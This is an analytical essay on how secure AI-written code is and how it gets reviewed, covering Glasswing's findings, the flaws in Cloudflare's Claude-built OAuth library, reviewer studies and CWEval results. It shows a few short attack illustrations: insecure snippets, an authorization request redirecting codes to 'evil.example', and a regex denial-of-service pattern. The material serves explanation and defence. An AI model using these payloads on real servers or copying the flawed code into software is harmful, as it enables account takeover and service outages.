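Some models write the warning themselves. Morkonda, Selim and Assal (2026), in *Security of LLM-generated Code*, examined 567 Python snippets from seven AI tools and came across insecure code with comments such as "This is HIGHLY insecure in a real application!". A more common problem was web applications that started in debug mode, which can let a visitor run commands on the server. In some cases, the tool had added a note about it:

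```python
app.run(debug=True)  # Set debug=False for production
```

A comment that describes code as insecure is much better evidence than one that describes it as safe. How much a comment should change a reader's mind depends on how much more often it appears with secure code than with insecure code, or the reverse. A line such as "validate untrusted input" appears above both working and useless checks, so it hardly helps to tell them apart. A model is unlikely to write that code is highly insecure when the code is fine. Such a comment also shows the reader where to look and what to change, and the reader can confirm it in seconds.

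Both kinds of comment can be out of date, because programmers often change code without changing the comments. Code without an admission may still be insecure, since most insecure code has none. Morkonda and colleagues give examples of these comments but don't count them, so it is unclear how many vulnerabilities a search for them would find.

They also argue that a warning is a poor substitute for secure code, because developers overlook it and put the application online in debug mode. They would prefer tools to turn debug mode off by default and add a comment on how to turn it on.

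### Thousands of vulnerabilities found in source code

The best argument for reading code is what AI systems found in 2026. In April, Anthropic, the company that makes Claude, started Project Glasswing, which gives selected organisations access to its Mythos model so that they can find vulnerabilities in important software. Anthropic also used the model itself to scan more than 1,000 open-source projects. It publishes running totals and a ledger of individual findings, which EconoTimes' *Anthropic Dashboard Lists 37,966 Vulnerability Candidates, 6,009 Confirmed Valid* (2026) summarised as they stood on 2 November:

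| | Findings |
|---|---|
| Suspected vulnerabilities | 37,966 |
| Reviewed by people outside Anthropic | 6,376 |
| Confirmed by those reviewers | 6,009 |
| Entries in the public ledger | 7,349 |
| Ledger entries marked as disclosed | 5,087 |
| Ledger entries marked as fixed | 217 |

Outside reviewers confirmed 94.2% of the findings they examined. Even if many of these were wrong, thousands of real vulnerabilities would remain, in projects whose source was already public. The models had access to whole repositories, so they could look up callers and definitions that a reader of a single function lacks. Such agents start with the source but can usually also run the program to check a suspicion, so this isn't a test of reading alone.

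Language models have also improved quickly at finding vulnerabilities. According to Anthropic's *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (2026), they found under 20% of the vulnerabilities in the CyberGym benchmark at the beginning of 2025 and over 85% in 2026.

The security firm VulnCheck is much more critical of the project. Its review emphasises that only 217 findings were marked as fixed after seven months, according to Poireault's Infosecurity Magazine article, *Anthropic's Glasswing Finds Many Security Flaws Yet Delivers Few Fixes* (2026). VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026) adds that Anthropic had marked 1,654 findings as duplicates and withdrawn 419. VulnCheck could trace 442 CVE numbers to Anthropic, about 0.5% of the year's total, and knew of attackers exploiting only two of them.

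The small number of fixes is better evidence of how little time maintainers have than of whether the vulnerabilities are real. Many open-source projects depend on a few volunteers, who can't repair flaws as fast as a model can report them. Cornelißen (2026), in *Glasswing*, compared the review with Anthropic's own figures and found only some of the criticism justified, partly because the public ledger omits flaws that partners such as Microsoft and Cisco find and repair in their own products.

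Two other objections to the 94.2% success rate are harder to dismiss. First, the maintainers of curl, a widely used tool for transferring data, decided that 19 of 34 published reports did not describe vulnerabilities, which puts the success rate for curl far below 94.2%. Different threat models may explain part of the gap, because a maintainer can agree that a bug exists but deny that an attacker could use it. Second, the 94.2% covers only the reviewed findings. Nobody outside Anthropic had examined the other 31,590, and their success rate could be quite different unless the reviewed findings were a random sample.

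### Finding vulnerabilities and certifying that none remain

None of these figures measures how many vulnerabilities the model missed, and the reliability of a verdict that a program is secure depends on how well the reviewer finds every vulnerability.

Suppose a reviewer has a 78.7% chance of noticing each vulnerability, the rate at which the models recognised their own flawed programs, and that these chances are independent. In a program with ten vulnerabilities, the reviewer will find about eight on average, which is very useful. But the chance of finding all ten is 0.787¹⁰, or about 9%, so an owner who fixes everything in the report will usually still have a vulnerable program.

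Two independent reviews can give a rough estimate of how many vulnerabilities remain undiscovered. If one reviewer finds 20 vulnerabilities, another finds 15, and 10 appear on both lists, then the second reviewer found half of the vulnerabilities on the first reviewer's list. If the second reviewer also found half of all the vulnerabilities in the program, there are about 30 in total. The two reviewers have found 25 of them, so about 5 remain. But two runs of the same model tend to miss the same vulnerabilities, which makes their lists overlap too much and the estimate of what remains too low. When both reviewers find nothing, the method gives no estimate because there is no overlap to calculate with.

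## Cloudflare's OAuth library: expert review and outside audit

Companies that don't trust a scanner or an AI reviewer with important code usually turn to human experts. Outsiders rarely see how these experts work, but Cloudflare (2025), a company that delivers and protects websites, left a public record when it published a login library written largely with Claude. In the README, the page that introduces the project, Cloudflare stated that security experts had reviewed every line and compared it with the relevant standards. The engineers also recorded many of their prompts in the commit history, so anyone can see some of the mistakes Claude made and which ones a person caught.

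The library implements OAuth, a standard that lets one application use a person's account on another without learning the password. For example, a printing app might want to fetch someone's pictures from a photo site. The app has already registered with the site and given it a list of *redirect addresses*, the web addresses where it can receive a reply. When the user clicks "connect", the app sends the browser to the photo site with the app's ID and one of these addresses. The user logs in and approves the request. The site then sends the browser to the redirect address with a short-lived code attached, and the app exchanges the code for an access token, a long random string that gives it access to the pictures. Cloudflare's library handles the photo site's side of this process.

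The code goes wherever the redirect address points. If an attacker can choose that address, the attacker receives the code.

### An encryption key stored beside the data

The library keeps a record of each approval, which can include data from the application, such as the user's name or tokens for other services. Cloudflare designed these records so that a thief who copied the whole database would learn only unimportant details. The library stores a hash of each token instead of the token, and it encrypts the application's data so that only someone with a valid token can read it.

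One approval can have several valid tokens at once. An engineer told Claude to encrypt the data a single time with one key, and to store a separately locked copy of that key for each token. The commit messages, which appear in the unsigned article *Reviewing Cloudflare's AI coded Workers OAuth Provider*, record what happened next. For a token *t*, Claude's first version came down to this:

```
ID of the token in the database = SHA-256(t)
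key that locks the copy         = SHA-256(t)
```

Nobody can feasibly recover the token from its SHA-256 hash, but a thief wouldn't need to, because the ID in the database is also the key.

The engineer noticed this and asked for a key that nobody could derive from the ID. Claude switched to PBKDF2, a function that repeats its calculation, here 100,000 times, to slow down anyone who tries to guess the input. That makes sense for passwords, which people choose badly, but nobody can guess a long random token anyway. The engineer rejected it as too expensive and chose HMAC, a keyed hash, with a constant *c* of 32 random bytes as its key:

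```
key that locks the copy         = HMAC(c, t)
```

Anyone can read the constant in the source code, but it doesn't need to be secret. It only has to make the two hashes unrelated, so that knowing one doesn't help in finding the other. A scanner rule for hard-coded keys might well flag it, because it looks like the beginner's mistake of leaving a secret in the code.

The engineer also noticed that Claude's code was storing an unencrypted "backup" of the encryption key in the approval record, as `encryptionKeyJwk`. In the commit message, the engineer asks whether this backup defeats the encryption, since anyone who has the record also has the key.

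The encryption was meant to protect the data if someone stole the database. With the backup in place it gave no such protection, even though the library encrypted every record with a respectable algorithm. Functional tests would have passed, because an application with a valid token got its data back either way, and a reviewer who looked for encryption would have found it. The engineer caught the problem by knowing what the encryption was for, which is good evidence that an expert who reads with an attack in mind can recognise a defence that does nothing.

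### The check that nobody wrote

Cloudflare published a security advisory for its OAuth library on 1 May 2025, about seven weeks after the project appeared on GitHub. According to OSV's *@cloudflare/workers-oauth-provider missing validation of redirect_uri on authorize endpoint* (2025), the library had not checked that the redirect address was on the app's list of allowed addresses.

An attacker could target a photo site user who has already approved the printing app. The attacker lures the victim to a malicious web page, which sends the victim's browser to the photo site with the printing app's ID and the attacker's own redirect address. Because the victim has already approved the app, the photo site doesn't ask for approval again. It sends the browser to the attacker's address with a fresh code, which the attacker can potentially use to impersonate the victim.

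According to CVEFeed's *Cloudflare Workers-OAuth-Provider OAuth Redirect URI Validation Bypass*, the attack works only if the site approves returning apps automatically. The application built on the library controls this, so the vulnerability depends partly on code that Cloudflare's reviewers never saw. The advisory rates the flaw's severity as medium, 6.0 out of 10. MITRE's *Missing validation of redirect_uri on authorize endpoint* (2025) includes an assessment by the US cybersecurity agency CISA, which knew of no exploitation on the day of publication.

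The library did check the redirect address later, when an app exchanges its code for a token, according to Wiz's *CVE-2025-4143*. By then the attacker already has the code. If the server compares the address only with the app's list at that stage, the attacker can supply the genuine address. A reviewer who searched the file for a redirect check would have found one that looked right but ran at the wrong stage.

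Experts could have reviewed every line, as Cloudflare says they did, and still missed this flaw, because the flaw is a missing check. Comparing each line with the standard reveals lines that break it, but to find a requirement that no line meets, the reviewer has to go through the requirements and look for the code that enforces each one.

The library's author says he knew the check was required and thought about it a lot during the design, but then forgot to make sure it was in the code. In a note he added to the advisory, reproduced in OpenCVE's *Missing validation of redirect_uri on authorize endpoint* (2025), he wrote that "he knew what he was doing but flubbed it". Having thought so much about the check may have made him less likely to notice that it was missing, since people tend to read what they expect to find.

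At about the same time, Cloudflare fixed a second flaw, in a defence called PKCE. An app that uses PKCE generates a random secret, normally sends only a hash of it with the first request, and reveals the secret when it exchanges the code. Someone who steals the code on its way back can't use it without the secret. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/@Cloudflare/Workers-Oauth-Provider package* (2025) explains that the library contained this defence, but an attacker could make it skip the check. Ordinary apps never trigger the skip, so PKCE would have appeared to work normally with them.

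Even without this flaw, PKCE might not have stopped the redirect attack, because the attacker starts the exchange and can therefore choose the secret.

Missing checks of this kind are common in OAuth code, whether or not experts are involved. Willison (2025), a programmer who writes about AI tools, describes using Claude on a phone in November 2024 to write a small OAuth script, which seemed to work. Somebody then pointed out that it never checked the `state` parameter, a random value that an app sends and should get back unchanged. Without that check, an attacker can trick a visitor into completing a login that the attacker started. Willison had reviewed the script far less carefully than Cloudflare reviewed its library, but both were missing a required comparison.

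### Neil Madden's outside review

In June 2025, after Cloudflare had fixed both flaws, Neil Madden published *A look at Cloudflare's AI-coded OAuth library*. Madden had written a book on the security of web interfaces, spent years in the group that develops the OAuth standard and worked as security architect at ForgeRock, a vendor of OAuth software. Madden reviewed the code briefly, during a day of meetings, and didn't present the review as a full audit.

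Several of the findings look alarming in the code but may do no harm in practice:

| What Madden noticed | Why it may be harmless |
|---|---|
| Scripts on any website may read the library's responses | The library doesn't allow browsers to send login credentials along with such requests |
| Some standard security headers are missing | Cloudflare's platform may add them |
| The library decodes the IDs and secrets of apps incorrectly | It generates these itself and can avoid the characters that cause trouble |
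| The generator of token IDs favours some characters | The bias is too small to make guessing practical |

In two of the four rows, a reader would have to look beyond the suspicious lines to judge them. The verdict on the headers depends on the platform, and that on the decoding error depends on how another part of the library generates its secrets.

The bias in the token IDs is a real mistake that can be safe to leave in. Programmers usually make it when they convert a random byte, which has 256 possible values, to one of 62 letters and digits by taking the remainder after division by 62. Since 256 is 4 × 62 + 8, eight of the characters each come up 5 times in 256 and the other 54 only 4 times. A perfectly random string of 32 such characters contains about 190.5 bits of randomness, and the bias removes about 0.14 of a bit, so an attacker gains almost nothing. Madden also doubted that anyone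 could exploit the library's version.

But to Madden, the bias cast doubt on the claim that experts had reviewed every line, or suggested that they had trusted Claude too much. It was in the first commit, and it is a classic error that an experienced reviewer should recognise. A reviewer may instead have seen the bias, worked out that it was harmless and moved on, but the history contains no record of that either.

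The most instructive finding concerned the *implicit grant*, an older form of OAuth in which the server sends the token straight to the browser without the intermediate code. The newest version of the standard drops it. Cloudflare's library still supports it but disables it by default. Madden found that the library checked this setting only in an optional helper function that reads incoming requests, not where it issues the token. An application that read its requests some other way would never run the check, so an attacker might be able to get around it, as with the check on the redirect address.

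Madden also criticised the tests, which covered little beyond ordinary use. The OAuth standard marks its requirements with the words MUST and MUST NOT, and Madden considers a test for each one the bare minimum for a login system, to be followed by tests for every abuse one can think of. A list of the requirements with a test beside each would have revealed the missing redirect check even if the author had forgotten about it.

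Madden also liked the encryption design, found the code reasonably well structured, and thought that human programmers often make the same mistakes. Overall, Madden thought the library was not bad as a first attempt but not ready for use. At ForgeRock, Madden had seen hundreds of security bugs in an OAuth product despite hundreds of thousands of automated tests, good scanners and careful expert review.

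None of this demonstrates a new break-in. Madden's review achieved less than the two earlier advisories if judged only by the vulnerabilities it proved, but it was more useful as a check on Cloudflare's account of its own review.

### How much review had there been?

Madden counted 21commits that one developer made straight to the main version on the first day, with no sign that a second person had approved them, so the project didn't use the usual procedure in which a colleague signs off each change. The encryption episode proves that somebody read the code closely, but the person who caught those errors was also the person prompting the model. Most software companies would call that careful programming and would still want a colleague to review the result.

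Cloudflare's account comes mainly from Kenton Varda, lead engineer of Cloudflare Workers, the platform the library runs on. He wrote in an online discussion that the work took about five days of heavy effort, with small commits over the rest of the month. In a comment that Willison reproduced on 2 June, a few days before Madden's review drew wide attention, Varda estimated that writing the library by hand would have taken weeks or even months. He also called the project a nearly ideal job for AI, because the standard is well known and the specification is clear.

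Those figures don't show how much of the saved time went into review. The published package is under 100 kilobytes with its documentation, so an expert could read all of it in a few days. Checking it against every requirement of the standard, and every way an application might combine the library's functions, would take much longer. The redirect flaw seems to be the kind of flaw that a single reading can miss and this fuller check could catch.

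Ory, which sells a competing OAuth product, went further than Madden. *Cloudflare, please don't vibe code your own crypto* alleges fundamental design flaws in the library, while praising Cloudflare's security staff as among the best in the industry. Ory gains if companies hesitate to use a free rival, so its overall verdict calls for some caution. But it also makes an argument that doesn't depend on who makes it. A reviewer has to build a detailed mental picture of the code, and that picture goes out of date faster than with a human colleague because a model can change a large part of the code after the next prompt.

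### Developers who aren't security experts

Cloudflare's engineers knew OAuth, chose the design and argued with the model about cryptography. Few programmers who use AI assistants are in that position.

*Plausible Is Not Enough* (Rahman, Alam and colleagues, 2026) summarises the best-known early experiment, which Perry, Srivastava and colleagues published in 2023. The 47 participants worked on security-related programming tasks, some with an AI assistant and some without. Those with the assistant wrote less secure code and were more confident that it was secure. The models of that period were far weaker than today's, so the result is weak evidence about the security of current code. The finding about misplaced confidence may be less outdated, because a better assistant gives people more reason to trust it and fewer chances to catch its mistakes.

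In *From Preventive to Reactive*, Bappy, Hossain and colleagues (2026) interviewed 15 software engineers about security between November 2025 and January 2026, then watched 14 of them complete programming tasks with Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. None of the tasks mentioned security, but each had a security problem. One task was to debug an upload function that wrote every user's file to the same temporary path, so two people who uploaded at once could receive each other's files.

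None of the 14 mentioned security in their first prompt, even though they had just spent the interview talking about it. (Elsewhere in the paper the figure is 12 of 14.) Only two of them noticed a security issue that the task hadn't pointed out. One was building a page where users update their profiles and saw that Gemini's code took the user's ID from the request itself:

```python
user = find_user(request.json["user_id"])
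user.bio = request.json["bio"]
```

Anyone could put another person's ID in the request and rewrite that person's profile. The safe version takes the ID from the login session, which the visitor can't edit. The other engineer simply asked Gemini whether any security concerns remained, and Gemini pointed out ways to overload the server that the engineer hadn't considered. (Deng and colleagues got little from a similar question in their repeated trials, so this may have been luck.)

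The sessions show how easily people who know about security leave it out of a request, but not how often this happens in real work. The sample was small, nobody's product was at stake, and one engineer said the result wouldn't have been good enough at work. The study also had no comparison group working without AI, and programmers forgot about security long before they had assistants. Bappy and colleagues found that experience didn't predict who would notice the problems. But their participants had one to five years of experience, so the finding can't be extended to someone like Madden.

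### Whether an AI label makes reviewers careful

Labelling AI-written code is one possible remedy if reviewers trust it too readily. Singh, Sovrano and colleagues (2026) tested this on 385 participants in *The effect of complexity and provenance on code review decisions*. Each participant reviewed a set of changes and decided whether to accept a proposed revision, which was sometimes correct and sometimes incorrect. The researchers varied whether the code was simple or complex and whether the label attributed the revision to a human or an AI.

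The label had no statistically supported effect, but complexity did. Participants accepted incorrect revisions more often when the code was complex. The label may have had a small effect that the experiment didn't detect, and the incorrect revisions weren't specifically security flaws. Still, the experiment suggests that a company would do better to split AI-written changes into small, simple pieces than to put a warning on them.

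Asked directly, reviewers say that the source matters a great deal. Rahman and colleagues surveyed 239 practitioners from 31 countries about how they review changes by people and by AI systems:

| | Human-written | AI-written |
|---|---|---|
| Would block a change if doubts remained | 19.4% | 43.9% |
| Count their own reasoning through critical cases as sufficient evidence | 28.5% | 55.2% |
| Would pause the review if it is unclear who owns the code | 14.6% | 29.3% |

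In addition, 61.1% said they require more evidence before approving AI-written changes. These are self-reports. The engineers Bappy and colleagues observed also described careful habits, often comparing the AI to a junior colleague whose work needs checking, but mostly didn't follow those habits in the session.

Rahman and colleagues describe two smaller experiments that don't clearly support either side. In one, 28 students checked and repaired code, and telling them that an LLM had written it increased some kinds of checking and improved some results. In the other, 37 students accepted changes slightly less often when they were labelled as machine-written, but the supposed author was a repair tool from before LLMs. Labels may help when people have to work on the code themselves and make little difference when they only accept or reject it, but nobody has tested that explanation directly.

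### What an independent audit adds

An *independent audit* is a security examination by people who did not write the code or commission the claims about it. They may examine the running system and its design as well as the text of the code. Madden's review was independent but covered only the source code and its history. The Cloudflare case gives several examples of what a fuller audit could add.

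Auditors normally start by agreeing on a threat model with the owner. Cloudflare had stated part of one in the README, promising that a complete leak of the database would reveal only unimportant details. Anyone who understands encryption can see that the backup key breaks this promise, without building an attack. A reader who didn't know about the promise might think that the encryption was only meant to protect data on its way to the database and that the backup key was a reasonable precaution against lost keys.

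The running system answers questions that are tedious or impossible to answer from the code. To test the redirect check, an auditor would register an app with one address and then ask for approval with another:

```
/authorize?response_type=code&client_id=printing-app
          &redirect_uri=https://evil.example/
```

A sound server refuses this request. A server built on the faulty version, with automatic approval, would have sent the browser to `evil.example` with a valid code. The test takes minutes and works whether the programmer forgot the check, put it in the wrong function or mistyped it. It would also answer Madden's question about missing headers, because the auditor would see the headers the platform actually sends.

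Reviewers can't settle some design questions by reading the code or running a simple test. OAuth 2.1 requires that *refresh tokens*, which an app uses to obtain new access tokens, either work only once or be cryptographically tied to the app. Cloudflare deliberately departs from this. If an app loses its connection just as it receives a new refresh token, a server that strictly enforces single use locks it out permanently, so the library keeps two refresh tokens valid at a time and cancels the other when the app uses one. As a result, a stolen older token can remain useful for longer. The code implements this design, and a test would confirm that, but whether the compromise is acceptable depends on what the tokens protect, so a bank might decide differently from a photo site.

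An outsider also lacks the author's memories. The library's author had thought a lot about redirect addresses and believed the issue was settled. An auditor who had never thought about them would have had to look for the check in the code. For the same reason, a second review by the same person adds less than the effort involved would suggest.

Outside reviewers lack the developers' useful knowledge as well as their harmful assumptions. Madden didn't know Cloudflare's platform, so he had to leave the question of the headers open. Good auditors get around this by asking the developers about the design and checking the answers themselves.

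### Reading and attacking find different vulnerabilities

Combining several methods in an audit helps only if the methods find different things. Matthew Finifter and David Wagner tested whether they do in *Exploring the Relationship Between Web Application Development Tools and Security* (2011). They looked for vulnerabilities in nine versions of the same web application, written by different teams in Java, Perl and PHP. They read each version's source code by hand, and they also ran an automated tool that attacked the application without access to the source.

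| | Vulnerabilities |
|---|---|
| Found only by reading | 52 |
| Found only by the attack tool | 20 |
| Found by both | 19 |
| Total | 91 |

Reading found 71 vulnerabilities and the automated tool found 39, so reading was clearly the better single method. But the readers, who were security researchers with all of the source, still missed 20 vulnerabilities that the tool found, more than a fifth of the total. The small overlap suggests that there were more that both methods missed. The tool is also dated, and a skilled human attacker or a current AI agent would surely have found more than 39.

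In *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Security Code Review* (2013), Edmundson, Holtkamp and colleagues, again including Finifter and Wagner, studied how much reviewers differ. They hired 30 developers to examine a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. Nobody found all seven, and the average reviewer found about a third. More experienced reviewers weren't reliably better. Reviewers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, so some of the difference between them was probably in how willing they were to report a problem, much as with the AI reviewers that became more suspicious after reading an alarming prompt.

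These reviewers were freelancers with a short assignment, not a specialist team with weeks to spend, but their results still show why "a security expert has reviewed it" tells you so little. If each reviewer had an independent one-in-three chance of finding a given vulnerability, all five would miss it 13% of the time, since (2/3)⁵ is about 0.13. In practice the chances aren't independent, because some vulnerabilities are obvious to nearly everyone and others to almost nobody. Adding reviewers of the same kind therefore soon stops helping, and paying someone to attack the running system is likely to be a better use of the money than paying a sixth reviewer to read the code.

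Using more methods also produces more reports that somebody has to assess. Cloudflare, which took part in Project Glasswing, later wrote that one of the hardest parts of the work was deciding which bugs are real, which are exploitable and which need fixing now, and that AI scanners and AI-generated code had made this worse. The code's owner may find it harder to act on an audit with 300 unranked findings than on one with ten findings and a working attack for each.

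### When an audit becomes theater

An audit of Cloudflare's library covers one version of the code, in the surroundings the auditors considered, and only the attacks they had time to try. Auditors who examined the library on its own might have dismissed the redirect flaw, because the attack needs an application that approves returning apps automatically. If they had examined one such application, they could have confirmed the attack there, but they couldn't have told the owners of other applications whether theirs were exposed.

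Of a review's limits, people most easily forget that it covers only the version reviewed. In March 2026, Cloudflare still stated in the README that experts had reviewed every line. The wording had not changed in a year and still included the remark that January 2025 was "two months ago". By then the library had gained several features, including one that lets an app identify itself with a web address, from which the library fetches a description of the app. A server that fetches any address a stranger supplies can end up fetching pages from its owner's internal systems, and Cloudflare requires a particular platform setting to prevent this. Experts may have reviewed that feature thoroughly too, but the claim in the README predates it and so is no evidence either way. Cloudflare had not qualified the claim after either of the 2025 advisories.

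Cloudflare's statement seems to have been sincere, and the commit history supports part of it unusually well. But a sentence about expert review at the top of a project, much like the comment about security above `set_language`, is weak evidence that is still likely to make people look less closely. The library's download page showed more than 58,000 installs a week, and few of the people responsible for those installs can have read the code.

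Owners can also weaken a paid audit deliberately. The owner usually chooses and pays the auditors and decides what they may examine, so it can exclude the riskiest component or allow three days for a job that needs three weeks. It can then keep the report private and truthfully advertise that the product "passed an independent audit". Customers can't tell this audit from a thorough one, so a careful owner gets no credit for spending more.

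Customers can tell whether an audit covers the attack that worries them if the published report gives the exact version audited, the threat model, the methods, the time spent, what the auditors left out, what they found and which findings the owner has fixed. For this library, they would look for an attempt to redirect an authorization code to an unregistered address, and for a note on which kinds of application the auditors had built on the library for that test.

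## CWEval: testing the same program for function and for security

CWEval, a benchmark by Peng and colleagues, runs both a functional test and an attack test on each generated program. An auditor can similarly test a login server's redirect check in minutes by sending it one bad request.

CWEval has 119 small programming tasks that cover 31 types of weakness. There are 25 tasks in Python, 23 in JavaScript, 21 in C++, 19 in Go and 31 in C, including 11 about memory errors. In each task, the model receives the beginning of a source file, with the imports, the function's name and arguments, and a comment describing what the function should do. It then writes the rest. Every task involves something risky, such as putting a user's text into a header, but the comment doesn't mention security.

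Using the same program for both tests matters even when a model gets several attempts at a task. *Activating Latent Security Knowledge through LLM-Guided Risk Analysis for Secure Code Generation* (2026) points out that some attempts may work and others may resist the attack without any single attempt doing both.

### Two reference solutions

A benchmark's verdicts are only as good as its tests, so Peng and colleagues also wrote an insecure and a secure solution to each task. They know what the tests should report for each:

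| | Functional test | Attack test |
|---|---|---|
| Insecure solution | Pass | Fail |
| Secure solution | Pass | Pass |

Any other result means the task is faulty. If the insecure solution passes the attack test, the attack doesn't work, and the benchmark would count vulnerable programs as secure. If the secure solution fails either test, the task may be impossible to solve and would unfairly lower models' scores. The insecure solution also has to pass the functional test, or the benchmark might never record a program that works but is vulnerable.

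An experiment by Al Mamun and Uddin shows what can go wrong without reference solutions. They had models write their own tests and then repair their programs until the programs passed. One test expected ten bytes of content from a five-byte buffer. Another required a function that lists a directory's contents to include the directory's own name, which is normally absent. To pass, the model changed a correct program to add a made-up line to its output. Running a correct solution against these tests would have exposed both mistakes.

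Reference solutions can't reveal everything a test leaves out. In the same experiment, a functional test for the header task used only the value `en-US`. Both a secure and an insecure solution would pass it, but so did repairs that rejected every value containing a space, including the legal `gzip, deflate`. Similarly, an attack test that sends only the pair `\r\n` will separate the two reference solutions correctly but still pass a program that blocks the pair and lets a lone `\n` through.

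Wu, Ge and colleagues (2026) added another check when they built *Last Secure Code Benchmark* from 150 real vulnerabilities. They pasted the lines of the official fix into the vulnerable code as comments and required the code to still fail the security test. They did this because many tests in the collection they started from inspected the program's text, and a program could sometimes pass just by containing particular comments. CWEval's attack tests run the program, so comments can't change their result.

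### Measuring the gap

A model writes different code each time, so researchers collect many programs per task. Suppose a model writes *n* programs for a task, of which *p* pass the functional test and *b* pass both tests. If someone draws *k* of the programs at random, func@*k* is the chance that at least one works, and func-sec@*k* is the chance that at least one both works and resists the attack:

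func@*k* = 1 − C(*n* − *p*, *k*) / C(*n*, *k*)

func-sec@*k* = 1 − C(*n* − *b*, *k*) / C(*n*, *k*)

C(*n*, *k*) is the number of ways to choose *k* programs from *n*, so each fraction is the chance that all *k* programs fail. A model's score is the average over all 119 tasks. For a single attempt, the formulas reduce to *p*/*n* and *b*/*n*.

Cannavale, Recupito and colleagues (2026), in *Smarter, but Not Safer*, added two measures, the *functionality-security gap* and the *conditional vulnerability rate*:

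gap = func@*k* − func-sec@*k*

conditional vulnerability rate = (*p* − *b*) / *p*

With one attempt, the gap is the share of all programs that work but are open to the attack. The conditional rate is the share of *working* programs that are open to it. *False Security Confidence in Benign LLM Code Generation* recommends the conditional rate, because the gap can make a model that gets better at programming seem to get worse at security. Suppose a fifth of a model's working programs are open to the attack. If the share of its programs that work rises from 50% to 100%, the gap doubles from 0.10 to 0.20, even though a working program is no more likely to be open to the attack than before.

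Suppose a model writes 100 programs for one task, 90 of them work, and 60 of those 90 also resist the attack.

| | 1 attempt | 50 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| func@*k* | 0.90 | 1 |
| func-sec@*k* | 0.60 | 1 |
| Gap | 0.30 | 0 |

The conditional rate is 30/90, so one third of the working programs are vulnerable. At 50 attempts the gap disappears, because only 40 of the programs fail and any 50 must include at least 10 that work and are secure. But the conditional rate doesn't change, and functional tests don't help a programmer with 50 programs work out which ones are vulnerable.

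The score at 50 attempts stays high even if secure programs are rare. If only 5 of the 100 programs were secure, func-sec@50 would still be 0.97, while a programmer who picked a working program at random would get a vulnerable one 94% of the time. The score shows whether a model can produce a secure solution, but the programmer needs an attack test to find it, and someone who hasn't thought of the attack won't have written one.

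The gap can also narrow because fewer programs work. Al Mamun and Uddin ran the coding agent Claude Code, with the model Claude Sonnet 5.5, on 48 of the CWEval tasks. When they asked for working code, 94.2% of the programs worked and 86.7% passed both the functional and security tests. When they asked for code that was both functional and secure, 88.8% worked and 87.9% passed both. The gap shrank from 7.5 points to 0.9, mostly because more programs were broken. The share that worked and resisted the tested attack rose by only 1.2 points.

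### 32 models and 380,800 programs

The largest study with CWEval appeared in October 2026. Santos de Moura and colleagues collected 100 programs per task from each of 32 models, using only the prompts that don't mention security. The models belong to seven families, and the researchers followed each family over three successive releases. The table shows how much the gap changed between a family's first and newest large model. A negative number means the gap narrowed.

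| Family | Models compared | Change at 1 attempt | Change at 50 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | GPT-4o and GPT-5.6 Sol | −0.175 | −0.148 |
| DeepSeek | V3 and V4 Pro | −0.094 | −0.160 |
| MiniMax | M2.1 and M3 | −0.056 | −0.085 |
| Qwen | Qwen 3 and Qwen 3.5 | −0.050 | Not significant |
| Z.ai | GLM 4.5 and GLM 5.2 | −0.046 | −0.077 |
| Moonshot | Kimi K2 and Kimi K2.7 Code | −0.037 | Not significant |
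| Google | Gemini 1.5 Pro and Gemini 3.1 Pro | Not significant | −0.107 |

The gap narrowed in every model family by at least one of the two measures, but it did not close in any of them. Among the newest large models, the gap at one attempt ranged from 0.13 for GPT-5.6 Sol to 0.28 for Gemini 3.1 Pro.

Google's models became safer for people who use their working code, but the gap understates this because the models also got better at writing working programs. Gemini 1.5 Pro wrote working programs 69% of the time and Gemini 3.1 Pro 94% of the time. Dividing each model's gap by its share of working programs gives the conditional rate, which fell from about 44% to about 30%.

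Upgrading didn't always narrow the gap. At 50 attempts, it widened in the middle release of Qwen, Z.ai and Moonshot before narrowing again. Of 22 comparisons between smaller, cheaper models and larger models from the same company, nine showed a significant difference, and the smaller model had the wider gap in eight of those. DeepSeek V4 Flash produced nearly as many working programs as the larger V4 Pro but fewer that resisted the attacks, so a programmer may not notice the loss of security.

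The study doesn't cover OpenAI's GPT-6 or Google's Gemini 4 models. It also leaves out Claude, because Cannavale and colleagues had already followed that family up to Claude Sonnet 4.5. Al Mamun and Uddin tested the much newer Claude Sonnet 5.5 on all 119 tasks, with five programs per task. Of these programs, 84.7% worked and 81.2% passed both tests. This 3.5-point gap is far narrower than any reported for the newest large models in the bigger study.

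Excessive caution probably doesn't explain Sonnet's broken programs. A program that rejects too much input usually fails the functional test and passes the attack test, but hardly any of Sonnet's programs did that. Most of the broken ones failed both tests, as a program does when it doesn't build or run.

Peng and colleagues published CWEval at the start of 2025, so newer models may have seen its tasks, and perhaps the solutions, in training. Santos de Moura and colleagues point out that this could exaggerate the models' improvement but can't explain why some weaknesses persist.

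### Did models get smarter but not safer?

Cannavale and colleagues reached a more pessimistic conclusion earlier in 2026. They tested 12 models on CWEval, four releases each of GPT, Claude Sonnet and Llama, with ten programs per task. In the newest releases, the gap at ten attempts was 10 points for GPT-5.2, 17.7 for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and about 25 for Llama 4 Scout. Llama's gap hadn't changed significantly since Llama 3.

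The title *Smarter, but Not Safer* fits Llama but not GPT or Claude. The researchers call the improvement in GPT and Claude marginal, at about 0.05, but that is roughly the size of the first step alone, from GPT-4 Turbo to GPT-4o. By their own statistical model, GPT's gap narrowed by 0.216 over the whole sequence up to GPT-5.2, and Claude's narrowed by 0.129. They ran GPT-5.2 with reasoning turned off to make it comparable with older models, and it might have done better with reasoning on.

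They suspected that models with downloadable weights were falling behind on security, but Llama was the only such family they tested. Santos de Moura and colleagues tested five others, and all five narrowed the gap. Gemini 3.1 Pro, which has no public weights, has a gap of 0.28 at one attempt, close to Llama 4 Scout's 0.296.

### New models with new mistakes

An average can improve while a particular weakness gets worse. One CWEval task is to search a text for a pattern that the caller supplies. Older models wrote a plain text search. The newest large models from Google, OpenAI and DeepSeek treat the pattern as a *regular expression*, which is written in a small language for describing text. This makes the function more powerful but lets an attacker overload it. An attacker can send the pattern `(a+)+$` with a text of many `a`s followed by an exclamation mark. In many programming languages,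 the search then tries every way of dividing the letters into groups. Each additional letter roughly doubles the time this takes, so a text of a few dozen characters can keep the server busy for hours.

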